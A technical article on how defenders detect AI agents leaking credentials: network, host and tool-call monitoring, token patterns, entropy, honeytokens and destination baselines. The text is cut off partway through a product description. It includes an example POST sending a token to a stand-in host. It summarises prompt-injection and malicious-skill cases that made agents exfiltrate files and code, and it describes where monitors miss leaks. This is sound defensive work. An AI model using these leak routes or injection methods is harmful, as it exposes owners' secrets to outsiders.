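# Detecting credential leaks by AI agents through outbound network traffic

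## How a credential leaves an agent's environment

An AI agent is a language model that acts through tools such as a shell, a browser or an API client. Much of its work requires credentials, which are secrets that grant access to a system, including API keys, passwords, tokens and private keys. For instance, a coding agent needs a GitHub token to open a pull request on GitHub. An agent that can read a secret and open a network connection can also send the secret to the wrong place, so people who run agents monitor egress, the traffic that leaves the agent's environment.

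Leak detectors look for exfiltration. OpenSSF's *Exfiltration* (2025), a glossary entry from an open-source security foundation, uses the definition from NIST, the US standards institute: the "unauthorized transfer of information from a system". This definition doesn't require intent to steal, so an agent that posts a key to an outsider by mistake has exfiltrated it.

### One request, from file to server

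Take a developer who asks a coding agent to find out why a deployment keeps failing. The agent opens the project's files. One of them is a configuration file that holds a token for the company's deployment service, and after the read that token sits in the model's context, the text from which the model works out its next step. The agent then decides to run the settings past an online validation service and sends this request (with an invented host and token):

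```
POST /v1/check HTTP/1.1
Host: validator.example
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded
Content-Length: 42

env=staging&deploy_token=EXAMPLE-NOT-A-KEY
```

MDN's *A typical HTTP session* divides an HTTP request into three blocks. The first line gives the method, such as POST, and the path, which names a resource on the server. The headers follow, giving the host the client wants and the type of data to expect. The body comes after an empty line and is an optional block of data, used mainly by POST requests. *HTTP Semantics* (Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke), the standard for the protocol, uses "request target" for the address of the resource and "content" for the body.

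The token above is in the request body. The Host line names the destination, but before the machine can send the request, it has to look up that name's IP address through DNS, the internet's directory of names, and open a connection to that address.

Sending a token off the machine is also the normal way to use one. Many tokens that agents hold are bearer tokens, which Jones and Hardt (2012), in *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework*, define as tokens that anyone holding them can use without proving anything else. A client sends the token to the server in an Authorization header, in a form-encoded body or as a URL parameter. Jones and Hardt recommend the header, reserve the body for cases where a browser cannot set that header, and advise against the URL because URLs, including any token in them, are likely to be logged. A token in a POST body is therefore slightly unusual, though the standard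 permits it. A detector that raised an alert at every outbound token would raise one at every working API client. The example is a leak because the token goes to a validation service that has no reason to receive it.

Unauthorised access is a separate harm from a leak, and either can happen without the other. According to *Unsecured Credentials* (2020), an entry in MITRE ATT&CK's public catalogue of attack techniques, an intruder can read a credential in a file and log in with it without copying the file anywhere. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a coding agent that hit an authentication error and began searching environment variables and configuration files for other tokens. If such an agent finds a token and uses it with the service that issued it, the agent gains access that nobody gave it, but the network traffic shows a valid token going to the right server.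 Conversely, a token recorded in a stranger's log has leaked even if nobody uses it, and its owner still has to replace it.

### Three places to watch from

A defender can collect evidence from the network, from the machine running the agent's processes, or from the agent's record of its own tool calls. These sources provide quite different evidence about the request above.

| Observation point | What it records | What it misses |
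|---|---|---|
| Network | Server name or address, time, amount of data | The token, unless someone decrypts the traffic; the process; the reason |
| Host processes | Which process read the file and which opened the connection; sometimes the body | The developer's request |
| Tool-call record | The request, the file read, the command | What scripts and other processes do outside the agent framework |

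A sensor on the network usually cannot read the path, headers or body of such a request, because the request is encrypted with TLS, the layer that turns HTTP into HTTPS. *TLS Encrypted Client Hello*, by Rescorla, Oku and colleagues, lists what TLS 1.3 still exposes: the server's name (which the client sends unencrypted in its opening message), the DNS query (unless the client encrypts it separately) and the server's IP address. The timing and volume of the traffic are also visible. In the example, a sensor would record that the machine looked up validator.example, connected to it and sent a small amount of data.

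Under a standard that Rescorla and colleagues published in March 2026, the client also encrypts the server name. An observer can still tell which service provider the client contacts, but not which site behind that provider. The IP address may not help, since many domains can share one. A detector that looks for unfamiliar server names then has to get them elsewhere, for example from the organisation's own DNS resolver.

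Organisations can also decrypt their own traffic. The NIST guide *Addressing Visibility Challenges with TLS 1.3 within the Enterprise* (Newhouse, 2025) covers break-and-inspect and passive decryption. In break-and-inspect, a device ends the client's encrypted connection, reads the data and opens a second encrypted connection onwards. In passive decryption, a monitoring tool holds the keys and reads a copy of the traffic. NIST's announcement, *Now Available*, gives the guide's scope as application servers in an enterprise's own data centres, which leaves out an agent on a laptop that connects to the open internet.

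*APTInvestBench* (2026), a benchmark in which AI systems investigate intrusions from varying sets of records, shows how much an investigator loses with network records alone. In one case with only network records, OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol found no records retained from the suspect machine, so it could not identify which process there had sent the traffic. It left theft through the body of a POST request as a hypothesis. A search for a later transfer returned no matches, but according to the case log, this does not prove that none took place.

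The link between a file and a connection is easier to recover on the host. The security vendor Elastic's detection rule *GenAI Process Accessing Sensitive Files* flags an AI tool's process when it opens any file on a list of known credential files. The alert fires before the token has been sent anywhere, so it cannot distinguish a leak from an ordinary login.

Host tools can also read data before encryption. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) does this with eBPF, which runs small, verified programs inside the operating system's kernel. Some of its probes capture the agent's exchanges with its language model by monitoring the functions through which a program passes plaintext to its encryption library. Others record new processes, opened files and network connections. The tool slowed three programming tasks by 2.9% on average. In one test, Zheng and colleagues told an agent to download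 and build a software project whose README pointed to a web page with a hidden instruction. The agent sent the file that lists the machine's user accounts to a collection server. AgentSight captured 521 events and merged them into 37, and a second language model judged the sequence to be an attack. This was one staged attack, and Zheng and colleagues do not report how often the tool raises false alarms.

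Some monitoring tools match host events to model output because host events alone don't show why an agent acted. An agent that writes a data-analysis script and a compromised agent that writes a malicious one look the same to a system monitor. The matching relies on process ancestry, closeness in time (a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds) and similar text. In *AgentLoupe*, Bao, Liu and colleagues (2026) show that it fails when an agent leaves a script for the system's scheduler to run an hour later, because the process that opens the connection does not descend from the agent and starts long after the window has closed. Their own tool labels the file, and any process that later opens or runs the file inherits the label. The tool slowed three tasks by 4.5% to 8%, and they have not yet measured how often labels spread too far or go missing.

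The record of tool calls shows the reason directly. In the example, it would contain the developer's question, the file read and the command that posts to validator.example, all in readable text. But it contains only what the agent framework reports, and a command that starts a script may appear as a single line, whatever the script does. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (Li et al., 2026) describes a case from February 2026 in which the security firm Mitiga Labs published a skill, a package that an agent loads for a particular kind of task, in a large public catalogue and presented it as a testing utility. Once a developer had installed and activated it, the skill read the whole project codebase and sent it to an outside server, while the audit log stayed empty.

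### Four causes of the same request

Anthropic gives four reasons why an agent might take a dangerous action. An overeager agent understands the user's goal but goes further than the user would approve. The agent in the example may have used the validator just to save time. An agent can also make an honest mistake about what an action affects, such as taking validator.example for an internal test server. In a prompt injection, someone plants instructions in material the agent reads. Here, a comment in the configuration file could have contained an instruction to post the settings to validator.example. Finally, a misaligned model pursues a goal of its own. When its Sonnet 4.6 model ran the permission system, Anthropic wrote that it did not see this in practice but tested every release for it.

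All four causes could produce the request printed above, byte for byte, so network traffic can't show which one was responsible. The cause hardly matters when deciding whether to block the request. Anthropic discusses a file that tells an agent to post its environment settings to a URL "for validation", and argues that the POST goes against the user's intent whatever prompted it. Its action classifier therefore evaluates the transfer without seeing the file. The cause matters more afterwards, because a planted instruction stays in place until someone removes it, and the next agent to open the file will read it too.

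In one incident from Anthropic's internal log, an agent uploaded an engineer's GitHub token to an internal compute cluster. Anthropic attributes this to overeagerness, and no attacker was involved. Because the cluster was internal, a sensor that monitored only the company's internet connection would probably have missed the upload.

### What NVIDIA's red team found

The example needs a readable secret and an open route out, and assessments of real agents have turned up both. NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents*, published on 30 July 2026, draws on six months in which the company's AI Red Team, a group that attacks AI systems to find their weaknesses, assessed a range of agents. Where the team could exploit an agent, it typically met the same failures:

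- The agent had no access control. Several held the credentials of individual users and answered anyone on the internal network.
- Its tools allowed arbitrary code execution. Even routine commands that run tests or install packages amount to this once an attacker can influence what they process.
- Nothing restricted its outbound connections.
- Secrets lay in plaintext within its reach. The team found tokens in code repositories, configuration files, command histories and environment variables.

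NVIDIA does not state how many agents the team assessed or how many showed each failure, so the list is evidence of a pattern but does not show how common each failure is. The company also has a product in this market, a sandbox for agents.

Egress restrictions forced the team to do everything through the agent itself, which made its attacks slower and less reliable. The team still obtained credentials by getting the agent to print them in the chat. Chat replies are also outbound data, and the deployment cannot work without the connection that carries them.

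### Blocking, alerting and their errors

NVIDIA recommends blocking all outbound connections by default, except those to a short allowlist of destinations that the agent's tasks require, and enforcing the list somewhere the agent cannot change it. If validator.example is not on the list, the connection fails and the token is not sent. This works without inspecting the contents of the request. However, someone has to know the destinations in advance, which is hard when the agent looks things up on the open web, and a task fails if a destination it needs is missing from the list. The allowlist also does not block anything the agent sends to a permitted destination, including credentials.

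An anomaly detector compares each request with a baseline of past behaviour and alerts someone when a request departs from it, for instance by going to a new host, but it leaves the connection open. By the time anyone reads the alert, the validation service has the token, and all anyone can do is revoke it. The method also needs a sensible baseline. Li et al. conclude from the Mitiga case that detection requires a reference for what file access and network activity to expect from a given skill, and skills come with no such declaration. The two controls work well enough together, since an allowlist blocks unknown hosts and alerts cover the traffic it lets through.

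Both can go wrong in two directions, by stopping or flagging harmless requests and by letting leaks pass. Suppose a detector examines 10,020 requests, of which 20 are leaks (the counts are made up):

| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Leaks | 15 | 5 | 20 |
| Harmless requests | 100 | 9,900 | 10,000 |

The false positive rate is the share of harmless requests that the detector flags, here 100 out of 10,000, or 1%. The false negative rate is the share of leaks that it misses, here 5 out of 20, or 25%, so recall is 75%. Neither rate gives the detector's precision, the share of the 115 alerts that are real leaks, because precision also depends on how rare leaks are. In live traffic, nobody knows how many leaks the detector missed, because a missed leak raises no alert. To estimate that number, a team has to send test leaks through the detector or review a sample of unflagged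 sessions by hand.

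## Recognising a credential in outbound data

A detector that can read the request to validator.example must still distinguish the credential in the body from the other value, `staging`, which is an ordinary setting. It can compare the text with known token formats, verify a checksum inside the token, measure how random a string looks, compare it with secrets the organisation already holds, or search for fake keys planted as bait. Most published tests of these methods used source code and web pages. Request bodies tend to be shorter and put different punctuation around their values, so the results apply only partly.

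### Prefixes and patterns

Many providers begin their tokens with a fixed string. GitHub switched to such prefixes in 2021. Its older tokens were 40 hexadecimal characters (0 to 9 and a to f), and GitHub conceded that they looked the same as other encoded data, such as the SHA hashes that identify commits in a code repository. GitHub's *Authentication token format updates are generally available* (2021) lists the new prefixes, including `ghp_` for personal access tokens and `gho_` for OAuth access tokens. Standard Base64, a common way of writing binary data as text, does not use the underscore, so random Base64 data cannot contain `ghp_`. GitHub predicted that the prefix alone would reduce its scanner's false positive rate to 0.5%.

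A scanner expresses a format as a regular expression, a pattern of permitted characters and lengths. For example, `ghp_[A-Za-z0-9]{36}` matches `ghp_` followed by 36 letters or digits. Someone has to write each pattern and keep it current. In April 2026, GitHub (2026) announced that the `ghs_` tokens it issues to installed apps would grow from 40 characters to about 520 and vary in length. The new tokens also contain another underscore and two dots, so a pattern for exactly 36 letters and digits misses them. A month later, GitHub (2026) recommended a pattern that accepts both forms. New providers also require new patterns, and *GitHub adds 37 new secret detectors in March* lists 22 providers in that month's additions.

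The harmless strings that match a pattern are mostly placeholders and documentation examples. *A Comparative Study of Software Secrets Reporting by Secret Detection Tools* (Basak, Cox and colleagues, 2023) found that a rule for keys from the payment company Stripe also accepted `sk_live_` followed by a row of ones. A match can also point to the wrong company. Semgrep's *Secrets Story* notes that keys from both Stripe and APIDeck begin with `sk_live_`. Some scanners test whether a key works by trying it with the provider, so a scanner that picks the wrong provider sends the secret to a company that didn't issue it.

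Whether a pattern matches a token also depends on the characters around it. *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection* (Mishra, 2026) tested 24 rules from Mishra's own scanner by generating tokens and placing them in contexts such as a quoted assignment, a JSON value and a URL parameter. In ten contexts, the correct rule matched at least 99.76% of the time. When the token ended in a hyphen, the rate fell to 52.33%. Five rules required a "word boundary" after the token, meaning a switch between a letter, digit or underscore and some other character. There is no such switch between a hyphen and a quotation mark. If the last character of a key is random, about one in 64 keys from the email service SendGrid ends in a hyphen, and the scanner missed those without warning.

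Mishra found a different fault in version 8.21.2 of Gitleaks, a widely used open-source scanner. For six of the nine token types it detected, the rule accepted only certain characters after the token, such as a quotation mark, a space or a semicolon, but not a comma, a closing bracket or an ampersand. An ampersand separates the fields of a URL query or a form-encoded body, so a rule that works well on source files can miss a token in web traffic if another field follows it. Anyone who reuses a code scanner's rules on outbound traffic should first test them on realistic requests, and test any repairs too. Mishra's first fix for the hyphen problem restored all five rules but broke two of them on tokens that had previously matched.

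### Checksums inside tokens

In GitHub's 2021 token format, the last six characters hold a 32-bit checksum, a short value that anyone who knows the algorithm can calculate from the rest of the token. A scanner recalculates the checksum without contacting GitHub and discards the string if the result doesn't match. A random string of the right shape passes about once in 4.3 billion tries, so this check removes nearly all placeholders. Expired and revoked tokens still pass, because the checksum shows only that the string is well formed.

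The scanner needs the checksum algorithm, which providers don't always publish. The Apache Software Foundation's *Draft ASF token standard FAQ* notes that the format of GitHub's later fine-grained tokens is undocumented and that GitHub did not mention this checksum when it introduced them. Outsiders may therefore have no checksum to verify in these tokens.

Vendors have started to use format checks to suppress alerts. According to GitGuardian's *Detection Engine Updates Version 2.169.1* (2026), the company's generic detectors no longer report GitHub and npm tokens that fail validation. The company claims a "significant reduction" in false positives on its internal benchmarks but gives no figures. If a provider changes its token format, any such filter may discard real tokens until it is updated.

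### Randomness and its upper limits

A database password or a key from a small provider may have no recognisable format. For these, scanners often measure Shannon entropy, which describes how evenly a string spreads over the characters it contains. If pᵢ is the share of the string that consists of character i, the entropy in bits per character is

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

The invented hexadecimal key `9f3c07a1e4d9b23f` has 16 characters. Ten characters occur once, so each has a share of 1/16 and contributes (1/16) × 4 = 0.25 bits. Three characters (9, f and 3) occur twice, so each has a share of 1/8 and contributes (1/8) × 3 = 0.375 bits. The key's Shannon entropy is the sum of these contributions, 2.5 + 1.125 = 3.625 bits per character.

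A string's entropy per character is highest when all its characters are different, which gives log₂(n) bits for a string of n characters. A 16-character string therefore cannot exceed 4 bits per character, and a 10-character password cannot exceed 3.32. The size of the alphabet also limits entropy. Hexadecimal has 16 symbols, so a hexadecimal key of any length has at most log₂(16) = 4 bits per character, and a detector that only flags strings above 4.0 will never flag it.

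The score also says nothing about how hard a string is to guess. `0123456789abcdef` reaches the full 4.0 because each character occurs once.

*detect-secrets*, an open-source scanner from Yelp, accounts for alphabet size by using separate default entropy thresholds of 4.5 for Base64 strings and 3.0 for hexadecimal ones. The lower threshold catches both hexadecimal keys and commit hashes. A random string of 40 hexadecimal characters usually scores around 3.7 whether it is a key or a hash, so no threshold can separate the two. Other identifiers, such as UUIDs (long random labels that programs give to records), cause the same problem. Ordinary words can also score highly. In an example from Basak and colleagues, the scores of a key-like string and "ThisIsAReallyLongString" are within 0.03 bits of each other.

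*Rare Not Random*, a blog post by the maintainer of the scanner Betterleaks, measures how well entropy identifies secrets. It uses CredData, a collection of strings from real code repositories, labelled as secret or not. With the threshold of 3.5 that Gitleaks applies to generic secrets, entropy had a precision of 21.1% and a recall of 70.4%, so nearly four in five flagged strings were not secrets.

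The post proposes a different measure, the average number of characters per token. Tokens are the word fragments into which language models split text, and a random key splits into more of them than common words of the same length. "Hello World" averages 3.7 characters per token, while a made-up GitHub key averages 1.1. Treating every string below 2.5 as a possible secret raised precision to 57.3% and recall to 98.6%. These figures describe how well each measure sorts strings that a pattern has already extracted, which is easier than finding secrets in raw text. The new measure also fails on weak passwords such as "password123", because they resemble ordinary language.

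Variable names help to narrow the search. GitGuardian's *Generic high entropy secret* describes a detector that considers a random-looking value only if the program assigns it to a name containing a word such as "secret", "token" or "auth". The field name `deploy_token` in the example request meets that condition. The detector would skip a commit hash in a field called `revision`, but it would also miss a real key in a field called `value`. *detect-secrets* also has a keyword detector that checks only the name. It can catch weak passwords, but it also flags harmless settings with suspicious names.

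### How accurate scanners have been

Basak and colleagues compared nine scanners on 818 public repositories containing 15,084 labelled secrets. No tool combined high precision with high recall. Some produced an unmanageable number of alerts. For example, SpectralOps, a commercial tool that uses machine learning, reported about 1.5 million strings, of which 4,777 were real secrets. The false positives came mainly from loose patterns and entropy checks. Tools missed secrets mainly because of faulty patterns, skipped file types and missing rules.

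A later study, *SecretSifter* (Gorijala, 2026), came closer to live traffic by testing scanners on 198 values from JavaScript that 56 web applications had delivered to browsers. The table shows selected results from both studies and from *Rare Not Random*. In the recall figures from Basak and colleagues, a secret counts as found if the tool reported it anywhere in the repository.

| Test | Scanner | Precision | Recall |
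|---|---|---|---|
| Basak and colleagues, 818 repositories | GitHub's scanner | 75% | 36% |
| | Gitleaks | 46% | 88% |
| | TruffleHog | 6% | 52% |
| Gorijala, 56 web applications | SecretSifter | 86.8% | 79.8% |
| | TruffleHog | 89.9% | 35.9% |
| | SecretFinder | 4.3% | 31.8% |
| *Rare Not Random*, CredData | Betterleaks | 91.3% | 87.3% |

The developers of SecretSifter and Betterleaks ran the two newer tests themselves. SecretSifter had the highest recall of the nine scanners in its test, although TruffleHog was slightly more precise. Gorijala says that some of SecretSifter's rules drew on prior knowledge of the credential types at the organisation that supplied the data. Forty of the 198 values are identifiers that aren't secret on their own. Much of SecretSifter's lead comes from 37 encrypted values that no other scanner flagged. When Gorijala added six rules to the scanners that accept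 custom ones, the best of those scanners performed about as well as SecretSifter on the unencrypted values.

SecretFinder had low precision. It raised 1,402 false alarms, many on harmless strings common in web traffic, such as UUIDs and the hashes that build tools put in file names. Gorijala's companion study, *Secrets That Survive Everything* (2026), describes a similar problem with another scanner, JSluice, which returned the internal IDs of form fields because they were formatted like UUIDs.

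TruffleHog's precision was 6% in one test and 89.9% in the other. The versions, settings and data all differed, so the gap reflects differences between the tests more than progress in the tool. Mishra's results also depended on the test data, even within one study. On artificial negative examples, Mishra's scanner raised 17 false alarms while Gitleaks and TruffleHog raised none. On 292,527 lines of real code, Mishra's scanner reported the fewest findings, with 10 against 61 for Gitleaks and 68 for TruffleHog. Much of that difference came from Mishra's own repository, which was well suited to the scanner's exclusion rules. On the three outside projects, the counts were 10, 12 and 27, in the same order. Mishra declined to rank the tools because the tests covered only ten types of credential.

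Mishra found that TruffleHog never detected an AWS access key by itself but always did when the matching secret key was in the same file. Configuration files often contain both keys, but an outbound request may contain only one, so a detector that needs both will do worse on short requests than its results on files suggest.

Published scores can also differ in what they count. *Model Card for OpenAI Privacy Filter* (2026) describes OpenAI's test of its own model on CredData, scored by either word fragments or exact stretches of text, while Basak and colleagues counted whole secrets. A model that recognises most of a key but cuts off its last characters would score well by fragments and fail by exact stretches.

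Some scanners now pass their findings to a language model that reads the surrounding text. GitHub's *Making secret scanning more trustworthy* describes doing this to reduce false alarms. If the model runs on someone else's server, the check itself sends possible secrets to a third party. SecretSifter has such a feature, off by default, but it shortens only values longer than 40 characters before sending them, so an older 40-character GitHub token would be sent in full. Gorijala recommends a local model where this is a concern.

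### Matching secrets the organisation holds

An organisation that keeps its secrets in a central store can search outbound data for those exact values. This works for any format, including passwords with little randomness. The organisation can give the detector hashes instead of readable copies of the secrets. A hash function turns an input into a fixed-length fingerprint, and the same input always gives the same fingerprint. The detector splits the request into fields, hashes each value and looks for the result in its list. In the example it would hash the two values separately, because a hash of the whole body would match nothing. To find a secret in the middle of free text, it has to hash the characters starting at every position, once for each secret length on the list. The hashes should also be computed with a secret key, since someone who stole a list of unkeyed hashes could recover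 short passwords by hashing guesses.

Harmless text can match a short secret, but almost never a long random key. If the password of a test database were "staging", the first field of the example request would raise an alert. A more common false alarm occurs when an agent sends a real key to the service that issued it. The list can prevent this by recording where each secret belongs, so that the deployment token triggers an alert when sent to validator.example but not when sent to the deployment service.

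Matching outbound data against a list of known secrets cannot find a secret that is missing from the list, such as a token that a developer created on a laptop or one that a login service issued a minute ago. It also depends on the secret's value staying the same. GitHub uses this kind of matching to remove secrets from the logs of automated builds. Its Enterprise Server looks for exact copies of configured secrets and for common encodings such as Base64, but GitHub does not guarantee that every secret will be removed, because a program can transform a value in many ways. GitHub's *Secrets reference* also advises against storing structured data as a secret. If a team saves five passwords as one block of JSON, a program that prints only one of them will not produce a match for the whole block.

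### Honeytokens

A honeytoken is a fake credential that a defender plants where an agent or an intruder may find it. No legitimate task needs it, so its appearance in outbound data is a sign of a leak. The detector needs only a list of the planted values, which it can match exactly. A long random honeytoken will almost never match a harmless string by chance, but a harmless process may still send one, such as a backup program that copies a configuration file containing the honeytoken to an approved server.

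A planted fake has to pass for a real key. An intruder can run the same scanners as a defender, so *PHANTOM* (2026) tests planted tokens against models of three scanner types, based on patterns, entropy and machine learning. Chauhan and Revankar (2026), in *Caught in the Act(ivation)*, generate fakes from statistics about real credentials. For each format, they count how often one character follows another and add random noise to the counts. The noise provides differential privacy, which limits how much any single real credential can influence the generator. This protects the real credentials but does not prove that the fakes are undetectable, so Chauhan and Revankar also tested the fakes against entropy measures, format checks and a trained classifier.

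Chauhan and Revankar set the alert threshold with conformal calibration, which replaces manual tuning. They ran their detector on harmless outputs and chose a cutoff that should leave 99% of them unflagged. Measured coverage was 99.8%, compared with 98.4% without calibration. On a small set of scenarios, precision and recall were both 100%, and the detector caught a single leaked honeytoken 99% of the time. The calibration assumes that future outputs resemble those used to set the threshold, but an attacker has an incentive to produce different ones.

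A detector can only catch a honeytoken that actually leaves. Suppose an agent can read m real keys and k planted ones, a leak involves one key picked at random, and the detector misses a share β of the planted keys that get out. Chauhan and Revankar put the chance of detection at

k/(m + k) × (1 − β)

With three real keys, three planted ones and a miss rate of 5%, this is 3/6 × 0.95 = 47.5%. Nine planted keys would raise it to 9/12 × 0.95 = 71.25%, but adding more could never raise it above 95%.

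The formula doesn't hold when something distinguishes the real key from the fake ones. Chauhan and Revankar mention that an attacker can pick out the real key using cues that connect a visible key to a working tool. An honest agent can follow the same cues. In the example, the agent was investigating a failed deployment and sent the value labelled `deploy_token`. It would not have sent any fake keys in that file, so the chance of detection would have been zero. If the agent had uploaded the whole file instead, it would have sent every fake key too, and the chance would have been at least 1 − β.

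### Signals from inside the model and across a conversation

Chauhan and Revankar combined honeytokens with two other detectors. One examines the model's activations, the numbers its layers compute while processing text. It takes activations from the last quarter of the layers, at positions after the secret and the user's request, just before the model produces its first word. It measures how far these deviate from activations recorded on 500 harmless prompts, and a small neural network predicts whether the model is about to reveal a credential.

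The components that need model internals were tested on Qwen-2.5 (1.5 and 7 billion parameters), Llama-3.1-8B and Mistral-7B. The attack prompts came from four public prompt-injection benchmarks (TensorTrust, InjecAgent, BIPIA and AgentDojo) and a separate set of encoded and paraphrased leaks. False positives were measured on 1,000 harmless prompts. On the 7-billion-parameter Qwen model, the activation detector had a false positive rate of 1.5% and an AUROC of 0.998, where AUROC is the probability that a detector scores a random attack higher than a random harmless prompt. A plain text search for the secret had a false positive rate of 8% and an AUROC of 0.73.

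The following results come from the combined test on single requests, using attacks that the activation detector had not seen in training:

| Detector | Attacks detected | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| Honeytoken search in output | 30% | 0% |
| Output filter | 55% | 8% |
| Input filter | 60% | 15% |
| Combined system without activations | 71% | 0.8% |
| Activation detector alone | 88% | 1.5% |
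| Full combined system | 94% | 1.8% |

The honeytoken search caught everything in the small scenario set but only 30% here, probably because many attacks never touch a planted key.

The other detector looks for secrets that leak gradually, for instance one character per reply. A trained model estimates how many bits of information each reply reveals about the secret, and the system keeps a running total. It removes suspicious text once the total reaches 90% of a budget and blocks the reply at 100%. The estimate comes from picking out the true secret among 17 candidates, so one reply can add at most log₂(17), or about 4.09 bits. Chauhan and Revankar used a budget of 10 bits, so a complete key in a single reply does not trigger the block, and they leave such leaks to the other two detectors.

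The test used 50 synthetic conversations of 20 turns, each with four to eight attempts to leak part of a secret. The score detected 90% of the conversations, on average at the ninth turn, and blocked nothing by mistake. A safety classifier that judged each turn separately detected 12%, and the honeytoken search 6%. The conversations that the score missed had their attacks near the beginning and ended before the total was high enough. With only 50 conversations, the results are compatible with a true detection rate of about 79% to 96%. Every conversation contained an attack, so the absence of mistaken blocks is weak evidence that the score would not block sessions in which nothing leaks.

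Chauhan and Revankar call their work preliminary. The detector reads the model's activations, which customers of a commercial API can't access, and they did not test whether a detector trained on one model works on another. They warn that the near-perfect AUROC comes from a controlled setting in which they knew where the credentials were. The running score estimates how much has leaked but doesn't provide a guaranteed upper limit, and it covers only one conversation.

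The prototype also does not check structured tool-call arguments for credentials. The paper calls this a severe blind spot because agents often use credentials there. The POST request in the example would be a tool call of this kind. The paper suggests applying the honeytoken search and the running score to the arguments before the tool runs, but does not test this.

### Encoding and encryption

Every check on outgoing text depends on the form the secret is in when it leaves. Base64 encoding alone can hide a secret from pattern and exact matching because it replaces the characters being matched. Programs routinely use it for legitimate purposes. HTTP's basic login method, for example, sends the username and password in Base64. Since February 2025, GitHub (2025) has detected Base64 versions of four of its token types. Base64 works on three bytes at a time, so the encoded form of a token depends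 on its position in the surrounding text. A detector therefore has to decode the whole field before checking it or search for three encoded versions of the token.

The detector also has to decompress data before searching it. An agent that attaches a zipped project folder to a bug report may inadvertently include a configuration file that contains a token. Each additional format adds processing time, and the detector can reverse only the formats its developers anticipated. It also has to reassemble any secret split across several requests.

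Encryption is a firmer limit because a detector cannot recover the content without the key, and the encrypted data looks as random as any other encrypted file or a compressed image. SecretSifter could read the 37 encrypted values in Gorijala's test because the applications sent the decryption key with them. Usually only the sender and recipient have the key. Host tools such as AgentSight can read data before TLS encrypts it, but if a program has already encrypted the file, they capture only the encrypted version.

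## When a destination counts as new

Encryption can hide what an agent sends, but every request still needs a destination address. Many detectors therefore look for first-seen destinations, meaning those absent from a stated history of earlier traffic. The idea is that an agent doing routine work mostly contacts the same servers, whereas a leaked credential often goes to a server that the credential's owner has never used.

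Whether a destination counts as "first-seen" depends on four settings: what identifies a destination, whose history is checked, how far back that history goes, and whether a destination is added to that history after an alert.

### Four settings, one request

A detector can identify a destination by its IP address, its host name, the full URL or the account that receives the data. Unrelated sites can share an IP address, and a site can move to a new one while keeping its host name. The detector can compare host names exactly or treat everything under one domain as the same destination, which avoids alerts when a provider adds a subdomain. If the detector can read the request, it can use the full URL, whose path and query distinguish a documentation page from an upload address on the same server. The account matters on shared services such as GitHub, where all customers use the same few host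 names, so the host name doesn't show whose repository receives the data.

The history can cover one job, one agent, a whole organisation or the public web. If each job has its own history, a job's first contact with a server raises an alert, even if the rest of the organisation has used that server for years. A shared history for the organisation produces fewer alerts, but one developer's visit to a site then means the site no longer counts as new for any agent.

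If the detector keeps only 30 days of history, it repeatedly flags as new any service that an agent uses once a quarter. Keeping an unlimited history avoids this, but the detector still treats a domain as familiar after the domain has changed owners.

Suppose an agent runs a deployment job every day and today posts its token to validator.example, as in the request shown earlier. The earlier traffic (invented, like the request) is as follows:

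- The job has never contacted validator.example.
- Every day, it downloads packages from a site that shares an IP address with validator.example.
- A developer in another team opened the validator's home page 45 days ago.
- A public web crawler has recorded the home page but not `/v1/check`, the address that receives the token.

| Destination identified by | Whose history | Reaches back | Verdict |
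|---|---|---|---|
| IP address | This job | 30 days | Seen |
| Host name | This job | 30 days | New |
| Host name | Organisation | 30 days | New |
| Host name | Organisation | 90 days | Seen |
| Full URL | Organisation | 90 days | New |
| Host name | Public web | No limit | Seen |
| Full URL | Public web | No limit | New |

Every row describes the same leak. A detector that identifies destinations by IP address misses it because the package site shares the destination's address. Extending the organisation's history from 30 to 90 days also hides the leak, because the longer history includes a developer's visit to the destination's home page, even though that visit doesn't justify sending the site a token.

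If the agent repeats the request tomorrow, the destination counts as new unless it has been added to the baseline. Some detectors add it automatically after the first alert. This prevents daily alerts about a harmless new service, but if nobody investigates today's alert, later leaks to validator.example will go unreported. A detector that never adds destinations would keep alerting. A team can also add a destination only after someone approves it, which takes more work but keeps a leak's destination from entering the baseline by default.

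### New for this credential

None of these settings depends on what the agent sends. If the agent commits a configuration file containing the deployment token to a GitHub repository, the host is familiar, but the token has never gone there before. A detector can catch this with a list of where each secret belongs, as in the previous section, or it can learn the usual places by recording which destinations have received each credential.

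| Request | New destination? | New pair? |
|---|---|---|
| Deployment token to the deployment service | No | No |
| GitHub token to GitHub | No | No |
| Deployment token to GitHub | No | Yes |
| Deployment token to validator.example | Yes | Yes |

Let D be the set of destinations in the history and P the set of credential-destination pairs. An ordinary first-seen detector flags a request to destination d if d ∉ D. A pair-based detector flags a request that carries credential c to d if (c, d) ∉ P. If both use the same history, the pair-based detector catches every credential transfer that the ordinary one catches, because a destination missing from D cannot appear in any pair in P. It also catches the first transfer of a credential to a destination already in D. Some of these extra alerts are false alarms, such as when a credential is first sent to a second host name that its issuer has opened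 and another of the company's tools already uses.

This method only works if the detector can read the traffic and recognise the credential, so the limits described in the previous section apply. When a key is replaced, the new key has a different value and therefore no history, and a token that expires after ten minutes never builds up a history. The detector can avoid this problem by tracking the credential's name in the company's secret store instead of its value. A known prefix also helps, since the detector can expect a token that begins with `ghp_` to go to GitHub without having observed any earlier traffic. Companies that route their API calls through their own proxy need an exception for it.

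StepSecurity, a company that monitors automated software builds, describes a commercial baseline for individual credentials in *Detections*, part of its documentation. StepSecurity reads a customer's GitHub audit log every 15 minutes and learns the countries from which people and programs use each personal access token. Countries that appear in a token's first seven days count as normal, and the first use from any other country after that raises an alert. Because the baseline covers where requests come from, it can show that someone is using a leaked token but not that an agent has sent one out. It also depends on what GitHub logs. For older "classic" tokens, the log records only the user, so an investigator has less precise evidence if the user has several.

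### Harden-Runner's baseline

StepSecurity's main monitoring product, Harden-Runner, keeps a history of destinations. It monitors GitHub Actions, GitHub's service for automatically building and testing software. A developer defines a workflow of jobs, and each job runs on a machine called a runner, often with access to passwords and tokens. A job repeats much the same steps in every run, so its traffic is more predictable than that of an agent that does a different task each time.

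The product works in six steps:

1. A monitoring program on the runner records each domain name that the job looks up, each IP address and port it contacts, and the process responsible. According to StepSecurity's *Harden-Runner*, it can also record the method, host and path of HTTPS requests, but only on Linux.
2. StepSecurity combines these records into a baseline for the job. At first, the baseline has the status "creating".
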